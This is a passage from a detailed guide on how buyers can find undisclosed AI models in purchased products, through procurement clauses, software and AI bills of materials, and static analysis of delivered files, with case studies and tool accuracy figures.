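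The final flow-down duty covers only subcontractors that handle government data. Will quotes Nvidia's Bruce Andrews, who argues that "obligations should follow the data, not the model's authorship." That is a fair way to allocate data protection duties, but it leaves a gap in disclosure. A company that sells a software library with a model inside may never handle the customer's data, yet may be the only one that knows what the library contains.

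### The UK, Australia and the EU

The UK has a simpler approach. The Cabinet Office's *Improving Transparency of AI use in Procurement*, a 2024 policy note reissued in 2025, gives central government buyers sample questions for bidders, including whether the products or services they offer use AI or machine learning. That wording can cover AI in a product sold as something else, and "machine learning" should prompt some suppliers to mention a classifier they would not call AI. But buyers don't have to include the question, and the answer is self-reported.

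Australia's Digital Transformation Agency publishes template clauses on AI that federal buyers can add to their contracts. The clauses cover both AI systems that the government sets out to buy and AI that a seller uses to deliver a service, so they can apply to a cleaning or consulting contract if the buyer includes them.

The EU's model contractual clauses for public purchases of AI, updated in March 2025, are also voluntary. One version is for high-risk AI and a lighter one is for other AI. Both are written for purchases where the parties have already identified an AI system, so a buyer that thinks it is buying vending machines would have no reason to use either.

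| Rule | Does it reach AI in a product not sold as AI? | Does anyone verify the answers? |
|---|---|---|
| US memorandum M-25-22 | Mostly not; agencies may add a disclosure question | Agencies test AI they know about |
| US GSA clause | Only language models that are a material feature | Mainly attestations, plus government tests of known models |
| UK sample questions | Yes, if the buyer includes them | Only if the buyer does |
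| Australian federal model clauses | Partly, through AI used to deliver services | Only if the buyer does |
| EU model clauses | No, in practice | The buyer can check the AI system named in the contract |

### How often suppliers get it wrong

As of December 2026, there seems to be no published audit or survey that measures how often suppliers' statements about embedded models are false. To measure this, researchers would have to ask the makers of a random sample of products the same questions, then take the products apart to check the answers.

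Mars gave a false assurance about the Waterloo machines, and Cadillac Fairview's first account of its mall directories left out a second model. Large companies can therefore be wrong about their own equipment, even when a regulator is asking. These cases don't show how common such errors are, because the known errors come from investigations that began after something had gone wrong.

The Federation of American Scientists' *How State Should Purchase AI to Ensure Accountable Use* (2026) analysed AI contracts from California, Florida and Utah and found that 77% of the provisions were standard boilerplate. Only 5.3% dealt with transparency and 3.0% with cybersecurity. The researchers had already identified these contracts as being for AI, so contracts for ordinary goods probably contain even fewer such provisions. The federation also found that states acquire AI by renewing broader technology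 contracts for products that now include AI features. It recommends requiring suppliers to fill in an AI fact sheet before every award and renewal. Renewal is a good time to ask the six questions again, since the buyer can still decline the contract.

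## Reading a bill of materials, and what it may leave out

A supplier filling in a questionnaire can report only what its staff know. A software bill of materials (SBOM) usually comes from a tool that reads the software's files, so it can include components that everyone at the company has forgotten. But these tools miss a lot, and a supplier can follow the official SBOM guidance closely and still leave an AI model off the list.

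### How suppliers make an SBOM

Most SBOM tools start from source code. Developers list the outside libraries they want in a file called a manifest. A program called a package manager downloads those libraries and any others they depend on, then records the exact versions in a lock file. The SBOM tool reads these files and converts them into a standard format.

A supplier can also generate the SBOM during the build, when a compiler turns the source code into a finished program. This can pick up libraries that were installed on the build machine but don't appear in any manifest. Other tools search the finished program for names, version numbers and recognisable code. Buyers can use these tools too, because the tools don't need the source code.

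The US and German cybersecurity agencies distinguish six types of SBOM by stage, from a design document to a record of the running program, as Reichmann, Krane and colleagues (2026) explain in *Poking Around in the Dark*. The stage matters for AI because an SBOM made from source code can miss a model that the supplier adds at the factory. Even one made from the finished product can miss a model that the product downloads on first use.

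### What the July 2026 minimum elements require

CISA and agencies from 13 other countries published their minimum elements for an SBOM on 29 July 2026, replacing a US version from 2021. Nine of the 17 data fields describe the SBOM itself, including its author, the tool that made it and the stage at which the author generated it. The other eight describe each component: its name, version, producer, identifiers, licence, relationship to other components, hash, and the method used to compute the hash. A *hash* is a short string calculated from a file, and any change to the file produces a different one.

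Suppliers should list every component, including those inside other components, and issue a new software bill of materials (SBOM) with each release. CISA says components can include AI systems and online services. A conscientious supplier would therefore list its models, but several provisions make it easy to leave them out.

The most important limitation is that a software bill of materials (SBOM) "may exclude non-code files". A model's weights are numbers rather than code, so a supplier can list the inference engine and omit the model it runs. The hash field also covers only executable files. CISA wants readers to be able to conclude that a newly reported vulnerability doesn't affect a product if the vulnerable component isn't listed. This is one of the main uses of an SBOM, but it doesn't work for models, because a product can contain a model that its SBOM leaves out.

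A supplier can also leave a field blank if it states whether it doesn't know the information or is withholding it. This helps buyers because the two cases call for different follow-up questions. CISA adds that buyers may treat an SBOM as incomplete if the author withholds essential data. However, these labels apply only to components the supplier has listed. If the supplier omits a component altogether, the buyer won't see a blank field.

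The document also adds no fields for AI, and checking whether an SBOM is accurate and complete is outside its scope. It does suggest scanning the finished program for unlisted components, which the next section covers. The minimum elements are guidance and create no legal requirements.

### Disagreement over what counts as a component

Even without these exceptions, two honest suppliers could produce different lists, because official definitions of "component" differ. Germany's cybersecurity agency, the BSI, requires a component to be a single executable file or an archive file. Reichmann and colleagues, who compare several definitions, read this as excluding an interface to an outside service, which a 2021 US executive order on software security includes. The SBOM for a product that sends its customers' text to a remote language model could therefore leave out any mention of the model and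 still be correct under the German definition, but not under the US one.

The researchers propose their own definition, which covers any part from an outside source that ships as executable code or runs with the product and could introduce a vulnerability. That makes sense for security, but it would still leave out an ordinary weights file. The people who designed SBOMs were mostly worried about vulnerable code, but a buyer may also need to know about a classifier that estimates customers' ages, even if it has no security flaws.

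### The G7 guidance on AI

The G7 Cybersecurity Working Group filled part of this gap in May 2026 with *Software Bill of Materials for AI – Minimum Elements*. The BSI, which led the work with Italy's cybersecurity agency, hosts the original. The guidance adds to an ordinary SBOM and groups its 50 elements into seven clusters:

| Cluster | Elements | Most useful content for a buyer looking for models |
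|---|---|---|
| Metadata | 10 | How and when the supplier made the list |
| System-level properties | 9 | The models in the system, and where data goes |
| Models | 13 | Each model's name, version, producer, hash and lineage |
| Datasets | 10 | What data the developers used, and whether it was sensitive |
| Infrastructure | 2 | Software needed to run the system, including inference engines |
| Security properties | 4 | Defences against prompt injection, which suggest a language model |
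| Key performance indicators | 2 | Very little |

Four of these elements are the most useful for finding undisclosed models. *System components* lists every model in the system, so a product with a face detector and an age estimator should have two entries. *System data flow* describes how data moves between components, including the interfaces of any outside services. A supplier that forwards customers' messages to another company's language model should disclose it here.

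The *model hash value* can be a hash of the weights file, which lets a buyer check whether the file in the product is the one listed. If the supplier doesn't have the file, for example because it rents the model from another company, it should mark the hash as unknown.

The *model description* should include lineage, meaning the earlier models that the developers built this one from. Lineage matters when a supplier adapts another company's model and renames it. The producer field also allows several names, so the supplier can credit both the company that first trained the model and the one that adapted it.

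These elements answer the first three of the six questions in the previous section: whether there is a model, which model it is, and where the data goes. They don't properly answer the other three. In particular, no element records what a model can do without a person's approval. The working group recognised that a system's level of autonomy was relevant to security but decided against a separate element for it, partly because countries may deal with it through other rules. A supplier could therefore complete every element without clearly stating that the product contains an agent.

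The guidance is "not mandatory". It also applies to AI systems, so a supplier has to recognise that it is selling one before it produces an AIBOM. This is circular in the same way as Waterloo's decision to skip its risk assessment.

### What a model looks like in an SBOM

The two main SBOM formats, CycloneDX and SPDX, both have ways to record models. This shortened CycloneDX example describes an invented door camera:

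```json
{
  "bomFormat": "CycloneDX",
  "specVersion": "1.6",
  "components": [
    {
      "type": "library",
      "name": "onnxruntime",
      "version": "1.20.1"
    },
    {
      "type": "machine-learning-model",
      "name": "visitor-age-estimator",
      "version": "2.3",
      "supplier": { "name": "Example Vision" },
      "hashes": [{ "alg": "SHA-256", "content": "9f2c..." }],
      "modelCard": {
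        "modelParameters": { "task": "age estimation" }
      }
    }
  ],
  "services": [
    {
      "name": "clip-summaries",
      "provider": { "name": "Example Cloud" },
      "data": [{ "flow": "inbound", "classification": "video" }]
    }
  ]
}
```

The first component is an inference engine and the second is a classifier that estimates visitors' ages. A buyer can find entries like the second by searching the file for "machine-learning-model".

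The "services" entry is easier to misread. "Inbound" means data enters the service, so the camera is sending video out. The entry doesn't show that the service uses AI, although software that summarises video clips almost certainly does. The buyer should ask the camera maker, which is Example Cloud's customer, which model produces the summaries.

SPDX 3.0 records a model as an "AI package", with fields for the type of model, its limitations and whether the developers used sensitive personal data. Unlike the G7 guidance, it also has a field for autonomy, which records whether the system can act without human involvement. The entry can be "yes", "no" or "no assertion". "No assertion" means only that whoever wrote the bill is making no claim, so a buyer should never read it as "no". Some tools insert it automatically. AIGen, a tool presented by Pepe, D'Amici and colleagues (2026), uses it when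 a licence is unclear.

If the camera maker deleted the age estimator's entry from the example, the file could still satisfy CISA's minimum elements for that part of the product, because a model's weights are not code. The buyer would then see an inference engine listed, but no model for it to run.

### Finding signs of a model in an ordinary SBOM

Most SBOMs have no entries for models, but many list software that would be useless or unusual without one. A buyer can search for the names of inference engines, model providers' client libraries (the code that sends requests to their services), and tools for building agents. These are some common package names:

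| Entry | What it suggests | Another possible explanation |
|---|---|---|
| `onnxruntime`, `tflite-runtime`, `llama-cpp-python` | The product can run a local model | Another library brought it in, and nothing uses it |
| `openai`, `anthropic`, `google-genai` | The product can send data to a remote model | The feature is optional and switched off |
| `tiktoken`, `sentencepiece` | The product splits text into pieces for a language model | The developers used it only for testing |
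| `huggingface-hub` | The product can download models | It downloads only datasets |
| `langchain`, `mcp` | The product may give a language model access to tools | It uses the library for simple prompts, or only to offer its own data to other programs |

The relationship field helps separate strong signs of a model from weak ones. If the product's own code depends directly on an inference engine, somebody probably chose it to run a model. If the engine is there because a general image library requires it, the product may never use it. In either case, the buyer can ask the supplier a specific question, such as "Which model does `onnxruntime` load?"

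Client libraries can mislead buyers about which company developed the model. Many companies offer services that accept requests in OpenAI's format, so the `openai` package doesn't prove that the data goes to OpenAI. Entries for agent tools are even more ambiguous. They show that the software's developers had the means to build an agent, but the buyer still has to find out what permissions the software has.

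If none of these names appear, that is only weak evidence that the product uses no AI model. A program can contact a remote model with the same general-purpose library it uses for any other web request. A phone app can use the inference engine built into the operating system, which the developer may not count as a component of the app. Some developers also copy source code into their own programs, where it no longer looks like an outside library.

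### How often the tools get it wrong

SBOM tools often disagree about the same software. Prado, Boinot and colleagues (2026), in *Mind the Gap*, ran three popular tools on 2,050 JavaScript and 1,276 Rust projects. They generated fresh lock files and measured the share of the listed packages that each tool reported:

| Tool | JavaScript packages reported | Rust packages reported |
|---|---|---|
| Syft | 43.78% | 100% |
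| Trivy | 32.71% | 83.85% |
| cdxgen | 98.72% to 99.91% | 99.34% to 100% |

The low JavaScript figures probably make the problem look worse for buyers than it is. The lock files included packages that developers need only to write and test software, so a tool that deliberately omits these gets a low score even if it lists everything the customer receives. Prado and colleagues attribute most of the differences to systematic choices like this, not to accidents. In *A Reality Check on SBOM-based Vulnerability Management* (2025), Syft and Trivy matched the lock files completely, possibly because that comparison treated such packages differently.

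Syft and Trivy produced an empty SBOM when a project had no lock file. If a complicated product has a very short SBOM, buyers therefore have reason to ask which tool the supplier used and which files the tool had available.

A longer bill of materials isn't necessarily more accurate. In *Beyond Compliance* (2026), GitHub's tool reported more Python and Java components than Microsoft's, but Microsoft's missed fewer real components and reported fewer false ones. *A Large Scale Empirical Analysis on the Adherence Gap* (2026) found that the tools it examined detected Python packages moderately well but recorded their suppliers and licences poorly. A buyer who searches only the supplier field for a particular AI company could easily miss it.

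The biggest gap is software that doesn't come through a package manager. Reichmann and colleagues tested five tools on six programming languages and found that they almost entirely missed components added during the build or while the program was running. AI components could easily be missed this way. Developers can compile an inference engine such as llama.cpp directly into a program, and the tool may then detect only the program.

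All these studies measured how well tools detect software packages. There seem to be no published figures for how often the tools detect model files, so a buyer has no good reason to assume that an automatically generated SBOM would list a model file.

### How complete are AIBOMs?

AIBOMs have a different problem, which is that much of the information they need comes from what the model's developer chose to write down. In July 2026, Erfan, Ryan and Rahman published *A Large-Scale Measurement of AI Bill of Materials Completeness*, which covers models on Hugging Face, a public site where developers share models. They started with 2,942,466 models, kept the 97,940 with more than 100 downloads, and generated an AIBOM for each one using an open-source tool from OWASP, a software security organisation.

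The tool also scored each AIBOM out of 100 based on which fields were filled in. The average score was 54.31, and the highest was only 68.70. Even these scores are somewhat inflated, because 20 of the 100 points are for basic fields that every file had.

| Category | Points available | Average share completed |
|---|---|---|
| Required fields | 20 | 100% |
| Metadata, such as purpose and supplier | 20 | 40.00% |
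| Basic details of the model | 20 | 81.75% |
| Model card | 30 | 19.51% |
| Links to outside sources | 10 | 68.02% |

The model card is the developer's description of how a model works, what data went into it and where it fails. Only 39.35% of the AIBOMs named any datasets, and 16.74% described technical limitations. Almost all of the 97,940 AIBOMs had text in the description field, but only 211 had a meaningful description. The others had placeholder text, which a simple check for blank fields would have missed.

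The autonomy field was empty in every AIBOM, though some developers may have documented autonomy. The field for intended use was also empty in all 97,940, even though Hugging Face pages often discuss intended uses, so the OWASP tool probably doesn't extract some of this information. Erfan and colleagues acknowledge that the tool's limits may affect the results. Either way, an AIBOM from this tool doesn't help a buyer tell an agent from an ordinary language model.

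The results are better for identifying models. Every AIBOM had the model's name, version and a standard identifier, which is most of what a buyer needs to look it up. But the researchers started from models that were already public and gave the tool each model's name, so the scores don't measure how often a supplier would mention a model hidden inside a finished product.

Developers can get better results by recording information as they train a model. Pepe and colleagues designed AIGen, which collects settings and measurements from training software and uses a language model to write the descriptive fields from code and documentation. In a small test on eight projects, they rated 91% of 124 fields as perfect or good. The language model sometimes invented details, so someone still has to check what it wrote.

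### What a signed AIBOM proves

A digital signature shows who signed a document and that nobody has changed it since. CISA's minimum elements include a signature from the SBOM's author. Some researchers have also built systems that sign a record of how a model was made.

*AIBoMGen* (Vandendriessche, Thijsman and colleagues, 2026) describes a prototype platform of the same name that generates an AI bill of materials (AIBOM) for a model by running the training itself. A developer submits the data, a starting model and the settings, but can't run other code on the platform. The platform trains the model, computes hashes of the inputs and outputs, and signs the resulting AIBOM. Anyone with a copy of the model can then compute its hash and check that it matches the one in the AIBOM.

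An AIBOM generated by the training platform is better evidence than a developer's own account, because the platform observes the training. Generating it also adds little time, taking about 0.4 seconds even when training took almost four minutes. However, the prototype supports only a few types of training and one software framework, TensorFlow, so most developers couldn't use it without major changes to how they work. It also covers only training, so it provides no evidence about what a supplier later put in a product.

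In *TAIBOM*, Safronov, McCaigue and colleagues (2025) propose a broader system that links signed records of the training data, code and weights to the software that runs the model. If someone replaces the weights after training, their hash no longer matches the signed record. The researchers warn that "trusted" does not mean "secure" here, since the system still relies on honest data providers and signers.

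Neither system can prove that a supplier has declared everything. If a camera has a signed record for its face counter but also contains an unlisted age estimator, every check will pass without examining the age estimator.

A buyer who can extract the model files from the camera can compute a hash of each one and compare it with the hashes listed in the AIBOM. A file with no match may be an undisclosed model, or it may be a declared model that the supplier has compressed or converted to another format, which changes the hash. The buyer should therefore ask the supplier about the file before making an accusation.

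### Are AIBOMs worth requesting?

Friedman and Leiserson (2026) argue for AIBOMs in *Driving AI Transparency*, a policy memo from the Institute for Security and Technology, a US think tank. Friedman previously led the US government's work on SBOMs, so he is well informed but hardly neutral. They say AIBOMs would encourage suppliers to find out what they are selling, and would let customers react quickly when someone discovers a problem with a model.

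The best reason for buyers to ask for a bill of materials is contractual. They can check fairly easily whether a supplier has provided a properly formed list. If the product contains something that isn't on the list, that may be a breach of contract on its face. A buyer who has only a vague promise of "transparency" has a much weaker basis for a claim.

In 2024 the security company Trail of Bits argued, in *Our response to the US Army's RFI on developing AIBOM tools*, that a fixed list can't capture important parts of training, such as the order of the training data. This is a serious problem for someone auditing a model's security, but not for someone who only wants to know whether the model is there. The company also warned that the Army's proposed AIBOM would miss models that a product reaches through outside services. The G7's data-flow element now partly addresses this gap.

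A bill of materials may also leave out trade secrets. Friedman and Leiserson concede that many of the largest developers won't reveal their training data, and suggest recording the missing information as a known unknown. A buyer looking for undisclosed models can usually accept that gap, because the model's name and developer are far more useful for this purpose than a list of the web pages used in training.

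Agents are harder to document. Friedman and Leiserson note that software can create an agent for one task, lend it a user's authority and shut it down afterwards. A bill of materials can't show what such an agent did, or what it could do at a given moment. It could at least disclose that the product can create agents and which tools it can give them, but the G7 guidance doesn't clearly ask for this.

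There is also no agreement on what an AIBOM must contain. Friedman and Leiserson criticise the G7 guidance for calling its elements "minimum" when none are compulsory, and for including open-ended ones such as "security controls". They propose a shorter starting list of 21 fields for government agencies to consider. But their sample contract wording requires an inventory for "AI systems provided under a given contract", so a vending-machine supplier that thinks it is selling ordinary hardware could ignore the requirement.

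On balance, a full AIBOM makes sense for products that the buyer knows rely heavily on AI. For everything else, it is better to request an ordinary SBOM and close the most important gaps in the contract, with a clause such as:

> The SBOM must list every file of model weights that the product contains or downloads, with its hash, and every outside service that receives customer data.

This is a much smaller request than 50 elements, and no one has to decide whether the product is an "AI system". The supplier should also state how it made the SBOM and whether it checked the finished product or only the source code.

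### The EU's Cyber Resilience Act

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act will soon make SBOMs compulsory for many products. It covers "products with digital elements", which include most software and connected devices. Its main obligations apply from 11 December 2027. Products already on the market by then are exempt from these obligations unless the manufacturer substantially modifies them. The duty to report exploited vulnerabilities and serious incidents began on 11 September 2026.

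The Act requires manufacturers to draw up an SBOM in a common machine-readable format, but it only has to cover "top-level dependencies", the components that the product uses directly. If a manufacturer buys a video library that contains an inference engine, it could list the library and leave out the engine. CISA's guidance is stricter on this point but isn't binding. Prado and colleagues add that a manufacturer's choice of SBOM tool could put it in breach of the Act without anyone noticing.

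Buyers have no general right under the Act to see the SBOM. The manufacturer keeps it with the product's technical documentation, and the authorities that supervise the market can request it. A manufacturer that chooses to share the SBOM with users must tell them where to find it. The EU's AI Act requires detailed technical documentation for some AI systems but, as Friedman and Leiserson point out, it doesn't require an AIBOM.

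A buyer who wants the SBOM therefore still has to ask for it in the contract. From December 2027, manufacturers selling new products in the EU will find it harder to cite cost as a reason to refuse, because they will need an SBOM anyway.

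## Searching delivered software for model files and the code that runs them

A buyer with a copy of a product's files can use static analysis to look for models instead of relying on the supplier's list. The usual order is to unpack the product, list the largest files, check every file for known signatures, look for inference engines, search the text, and then confirm and identify anything suspicious.

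### Unpacking the product

Most software arrives as one file that contains many others. An Android app, for example, is an APK file, a type of ZIP archive. Liu and colleagues searched three parts of the APK: the `.dex` files, which hold the app's main code; the `lib` folder, which holds *native libraries* compiled for the phone's processor; and the `assets` folder, which holds other files the app needs. Researchers often unpack apps with the free program Apktool, as in *Stealthy Backdoor Attack to Real-world Models in Android Apps* (2025).

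Desktop installers and firmware images need different tools, but both often contain archives inside other archives, so the analyst has to keep unpacking until none are left. To check a device like the Waterloo vending machines, the buyer would need the firmware or a copy of the machine's disk.

Careless unpacking can damage the model files a buyer is looking for. Agyemang and colleagues found that extracting files from Apple's firmware archives could alter bytes and break some of the models. They avoided this by mounting each firmware image as a disk and copying the files from it.

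### Large files and file signatures

Sorting the unpacked files by size takes minutes and will often reveal a language model. Even Phi-4 Mini, a small language model that the developers in *Less Is More* considered for their phone app, takes up 3,910 MB. Apart from videos, databases and disk images, few other files in ordinary business software are that big. Sorting by size will miss most classifiers, because they are much smaller.

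The next step is to check the opening bytes of every file. Many formats put a fixed sequence of characters, called a *signature*, near the start so that programs can recognise the file. This works even when the file has an uninformative name like `data.bin`. A LiteRT model has the characters `TFL3` at byte offset 4, which is the fifth byte because counting starts at zero:

```text
Offset:  0   1   2   3   4   5   6   7
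Value:   1c  00  00  00  54  46  4c  33
Text:    .   .   .   .   T   F   L   3
```

Guyomard, Mauvisseau and Paindavoine (2025), in *Breaking SafetyCore*, list identifying features for four common formats. The table adds four more types of file:

| Format | What to look for | Reliability |
|---|---|---|
| LiteRT (formerly TensorFlow Lite) | `TFL3` at offset 4 | Good |
| GGUF, used by llama.cpp | `GGUF` at offset 0 | Good |
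| ExecuTorch | `ET` and two digits at offset 4, followed by `eh` and two digits | Good |
| TorchScript | A ZIP archive containing `code` and `data` folders, `data.pkl` and `constants.pkl` | Good, but only after opening the archive |
| safetensors | An eight-byte number, then `{` at offset 8 | Weak until the analyst reads the header |
| ONNX | No fixed opening bytes; sometimes the text `onnx::` | Weak |
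| Compiled Core ML (Apple) | A folder ending in `.mlmodelc` that contains `coremldata.bin` | Depends on file names |
| Raw weights | Nothing | None |

GGUF is the most convenient of these formats for a buyer. Its specification, Debian's *gguf.md*, requires each file to include the model's architecture and recommends fields for its name, author, organisation and licence. If the developer filled them in, the analyst can read what the model is without running it. But anyone who converts or edits the file can change these fields, so the analyst can't rely on them alone.

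A safetensors file has no signature of its own. According to Hugging Face's *Crate safetensors*, its first eight bytes give the length of a header, which must begin with `{`. Other files can have that character in the same place by chance, so the analyst should check that the length makes sense and then read the header. In a real model, the header lists the blocks of weights. Hugging Face's *Safetensors documentation* shows the header of GPT-2, an early language model, with entries such as `h.10.ln_1.weight` that clearly belong to a neural network.

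ONNX is harder to recognise because it uses Protocol Buffers, a general-purpose format that has no signature. Guyomard and colleagues suggest searching for `onnx::`, but this text is typical of models exported from PyTorch, and other ONNX files may lack it. *Transposing tensor files*, on mmapped.blog, explains that Protocol Buffers files can't exceed two gigabytes, so larger ONNX models have to keep their weights in a separate file. A search could therefore find a small ONNX file and miss the huge unlabelled file beside it.

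For raw weights, the only option is to check whether the contents look like weights. Agyemang and colleagues took a sample of up to 64 KiB from each file and read it as 32-bit decimal numbers. A file passed if at least 95% of the values were finite and their standard deviation was below a million. This test found the 281 files of apparently raw weights mentioned earlier, but 43 of them passed only because all the sampled values were identical, as they would be in a block of zeros. A stricter test that excluded these left 238 files.

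### Inference engines

Inference engines are easier to search for than models because there are fewer engines. Guyomard and colleagues explain that writing fast code for every type of processor is difficult, so most companies use one of a handful of engines, usually an open-source one. In an Android app, the `lib` folder may contain a file with an obvious name, such as `libtensorflowlite_jni.so` or `libonnxruntime.so`. If the developer has compiled the engine into a larger program, the engine's error messages and function names may still be in that program as readable text.

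Finding an engine without a model file is a good reason to question the supplier, because the model's weights may be encrypted or be delivered later. Some apps contain a model but no engine, because they use the one built into the phone.

### Addresses, keys and prompts

A program that contacts a remote model directly needs the service's address. Analysts can search the unpacked files for addresses such as `api.openai.com`, `api.anthropic.com` and `generativelanguage.googleapis.com`, which belong to OpenAI, Anthropic and Google. The search should include native libraries, because Liu and colleagues found that some developers put their calls to OpenAI there, where an older scanning tool couldn't detect them.

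Some programs also contain an *access key*, a password-like code that the provider uses to identify and bill the customer. A buyer who finds one should tell the supplier and not use it, since using someone else's key may be illegal.

Stored prompts, the written instructions a program sends to a language model, are often the most informative text in the software. A prompt such as "Rate this applicant's honesty from 1 to 10" would show that the product uses a language model to rate applicants' honesty. If the prompt also includes instructions for sending emails or running commands, the product may contain an agent.

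None of these matches is conclusive. For example, the security company Akamai describes malware whose own server address imitated the address format of a chat model's service. Someone therefore has to read the code around a match to see what that code does.

### Confirming and identifying a model

The best way to confirm that a file is a model is to load it into an inference engine. *Stealthy Backdoor Attack to Real-world Models in Android Apps* picked out files with suitable extensions, then discarded any that failed to load. In *THEMIS*, a study of how to watermark models inside apps, Huang, Zhang and colleagues (2025) also ran each extracted model on random data to make sure it worked. A successful load usually reveals the shape of the model's inputs and outputs, which is a strong clue to its purpose.

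A failed load is only weak evidence that a file is not a model. Agyemang and colleagues tried to run 855 of Apple's compiled model bundles, including copies of the same model from different products. They converted 155 into a format that ordinary tools could load, and another 566 worked through Apple's own software. The remaining 134, or 16%, failed even though Apple had shipped them as models. One hand-gesture model crashed the loading program every time. Files in some formats can execute code when opened, so analysts should load unknown models on an isolated computer.

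Once the analyst has a working model, they can try to find out whose it is. Hugging Face publishes a hash for each large model file it hosts, and if the delivered file has the same hash, the two files are almost certainly identical. The supplier may have converted or retrained the model, which would change the hash, so a mismatch proves very little. Further training often leaves a model's structure unchanged, so comparing the names and sizes of its blocks of weights can still suggest which public model it came from.

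Hashing the weights separately from the files that describe them helps identify copies of the same model. Agyemang and colleagues found three models on Apple TV that had the same weights as the copies on other Apple devices and differed only in an internal build label.

### Android SafetyCore

SafetyCore is an example of how an analyst can find a model in a product that people already own. Google introduced it in November 2024 as an Android system service, a background component that other apps can use. Phones received it through Google's background updates, and many owners found out only when they noticed an unfamiliar name in their list of apps. Google said that SafetyCore classifies content on the phone, and only when an app requests this through an optional feature. At first, only Google Messages used it, to blur images that might contain nudity and display a warning.

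Guyomard and colleagues, from the French company Skyld AI, examined SafetyCore on a Pixel 6 phone running Android 15. They searched the files the service had downloaded and quickly found one with `TFL3` at offset 4, which identified it as a LiteRT model.

The researchers then worked out what the model did. Its input had the shape 1 × 224 × 224 × 3, which fits one 224 × 224 pixel image with three colour values per pixel. Its output was four numbers. When the researchers gave it explicit images, some of these numbers rose above 0.5, while for other images they stayed below. The model was a narrow classifier, not a language model or an agent. Its last step scored each label separately, so one image could receive several labels.

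These results fit Google's description of the model's purpose. They can't confirm that SafetyCore runs only when an app calls it or that its results stay on the phone, which depend on the surrounding software. The case was also easier than most because the researchers already knew which service to examine and the model was unencrypted. They found the model among the downloaded files, so a buyer who searched only the installer might have missed it.

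### How well app scanners work

Researchers have scanned Android apps for AI for years. Two early tools were DL Sniffer, which examined 16,500 apps, and ModelXRay, which examined 46,753. AI Discriminator later searched decompiled apps for keywords and identified 56,682 AI apps among 7,259,232, or about 0.8%. These figures are now mainly of historical interest because the tools depended on lists of known names, and many of the apps predate the spread of language models.

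Liu and colleagues designed LLMAID to reduce this dependence on fixed lists. It extracts the names of code packages, functions, model files and web addresses from an app and removes those already known to be unrelated to AI. It then prompts a language model, GPT-3.5-turbo, to explain what each remaining component does and classify it as AI or not. The language model can often interpret names that are not on any list. For example, it correctly explained that `nlp.WordPieceModelPB` splits text into pieces.

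The researchers tested LLMAID on 382 apps that AI Discriminator had already identified as using AI. Two of the researchers independently labelled 49,371 components by hand. LLMAID's precision was 98.05%, so almost everything it flagged was AI, and its recall was 93.31%, so it missed about 7% of the AI components. In a second test, on the 3,819 apps described earlier, its precision was 97.32% and its recall was 91.01%.

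| Result for the same 3,819 apps | AI Discriminator | LLMAID |
|---|---|---|
| Apps identified as containing AI | 603 | 1,366 |
| Share of all the apps | 15.8% | 35.8% |

LLMAID therefore found about 2.3 times as many AI apps. The paper's figure of "242% more" is an arithmetic error; the increase is 127%. The researchers took apart 86 of the 820 apps that only LLMAID had flagged and confirmed that 83 contained AI.

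The recall figures probably overstate how well LLMAID would work for a buyer. They cover only components that LLMAID extracted, so a model hidden inside an encrypted file would not count as a miss. LLMAID also relies heavily on names. It missed two apps that each contained a single LiteRT file and little else to suggest AI, and four whose only clue was a file ending in `.model`. A simple signature check would have found the two LiteRT files, so buyers should use both methods.

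An "AI app" here also means any app with at least one AI component, even if that component is a library the app never uses. About 27% of the AI components were for data analysis, including general code for handling the grids of numbers that models use. Computer vision accounted for 55%, and about a sixth of those components were for face recognition. A buyer concerned only about face recognition could therefore ignore most of the matches.

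Scanning is fast enough to do routinely. LLMAID took an average of 639 seconds per app, so 200 apps would need about 35 hours of computer time. A faster version took 227 seconds and identified 371 of the 382 known AI apps, compared with 378 for the full version. GPT-3.5-turbo is long out of date, and a current model might well make fewer mistakes. Even so, *Mobile App Analysis in the New Era* (2026), a survey of the field, found that researchers had made only limited use of language models for static analysis of mobile apps.

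There seem to be no comparable accuracy figures for desktop software or for the firmware of cameras and similar devices.

### Searching for keys and prompts in malware

Security companies have shown that text searches can find calls to language models in very large collections of files. In *LLM-Enabled Malware In the Wild*, Delamotte and Bernadett-Shapiro describe how SentinelLABS, the research arm of the security company SentinelOne, searched for malware that uses a language model while it runs. Such malware usually contains an access key and written prompts, which are hard to disguise.

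A provider's keys follow a recognisable pattern. OpenAI's, for example, include a fixed identifier in Base64, a way of encoding data as text. The researchers wrote rules to search for these patterns in YARA, a language for searching files, and ran them on a year of files from VirusTotal, a service for checking suspicious files. They found more than 7,000 files containing over 6,000 different keys.

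Most of these files were not malicious. *Researchers expose MalTerminal, an LLM-enabled malware pioneer* (Paganini, 2025) reports that most of the keys had leaked from harmless software. The harmless files were a nuisance for the malware researchers, but they are encouraging for buyers, who are looking for ordinary software that calls a model.

The researchers also searched for prompts and used small language-model classifiers to judge whether each one had a malicious purpose. This helped them find MalTerminal, a Windows program that uses GPT-4 to write ransomware or code for controlling a computer remotely. A person chooses which one it writes, so it is closer to an ordinary language-model tool than an agent. The program contained an address that OpenAI deprecated in early November 2023, which suggests it was written before then, according to The Hacker News (2025). There was no evidence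 that anyone had used it in an attack.

Paganini reports that the prompt search also found tools for navigating websites and controlling phone screens. These tools are more like agents, so the same method could help buyers look for undisclosed agents.

In a later, larger search, the security company Arctic Wolf found 22,331 malware files between February 2025 and February 2026 that matched its rules for signs of AI. Only about 8% appeared to call a language model while running, and about 7% contained access keys. Many of the others matched because they had features, such as tutorial-style comments, that suggested an AI had written the code. Buyers should distinguish AI-written code from code that uses a model, because a program that AI helped to write may not contain one.

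These figures don't show that malware with a built-in model is common. Unit 42's *The State of AI-Enabled Malware August 2026* (2026) examined 405 samples with some connection to AI and found only 12 on customers' computers. Some samples merely used a name such as ChatGPT to attract victims. Unit 42 belongs to Palo Alto Networks, which sells security software, so it has little commercial reason to play down the threat.

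The searches show that software can check a huge number of files for keys and prompts, but nobody knows how many programs they missed. They may also work less well on commercial products than on malware. If the supplier's own server passes the data to the model, the provider's address, the access key and the prompts can all stay on that server.

### What static analysis misses

Encryption is the most common obstacle. An encrypted model has no visible signature or structure, and vendors may encrypt one for innocent reasons, such as protecting an expensive model from competitors. The ModelXRay study, now several years old, found that 41% of apps with machine learning left their models unprotected. This suggests that most had some protection, which is a reason not to rely on a signature search alone.

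An encrypted file may still stand out if it is large and its contents look random. The buyer can ask the supplier what it is. A specialist with full control of the device may also be able to copy the model from memory after the product decrypts it. In a pilot study for THEMIS, however, Huang and colleagues found that an earlier method of this kind failed on nearly half of the encrypted models they tried. Some copies lacked essential information about inputs and outputs, and some apps used decryption code that the tool didn't recognise. The *SoK* survey by Huang and colleagues describes a harder case, in which a phone runs all or part of the model in a protected area of its hardware.

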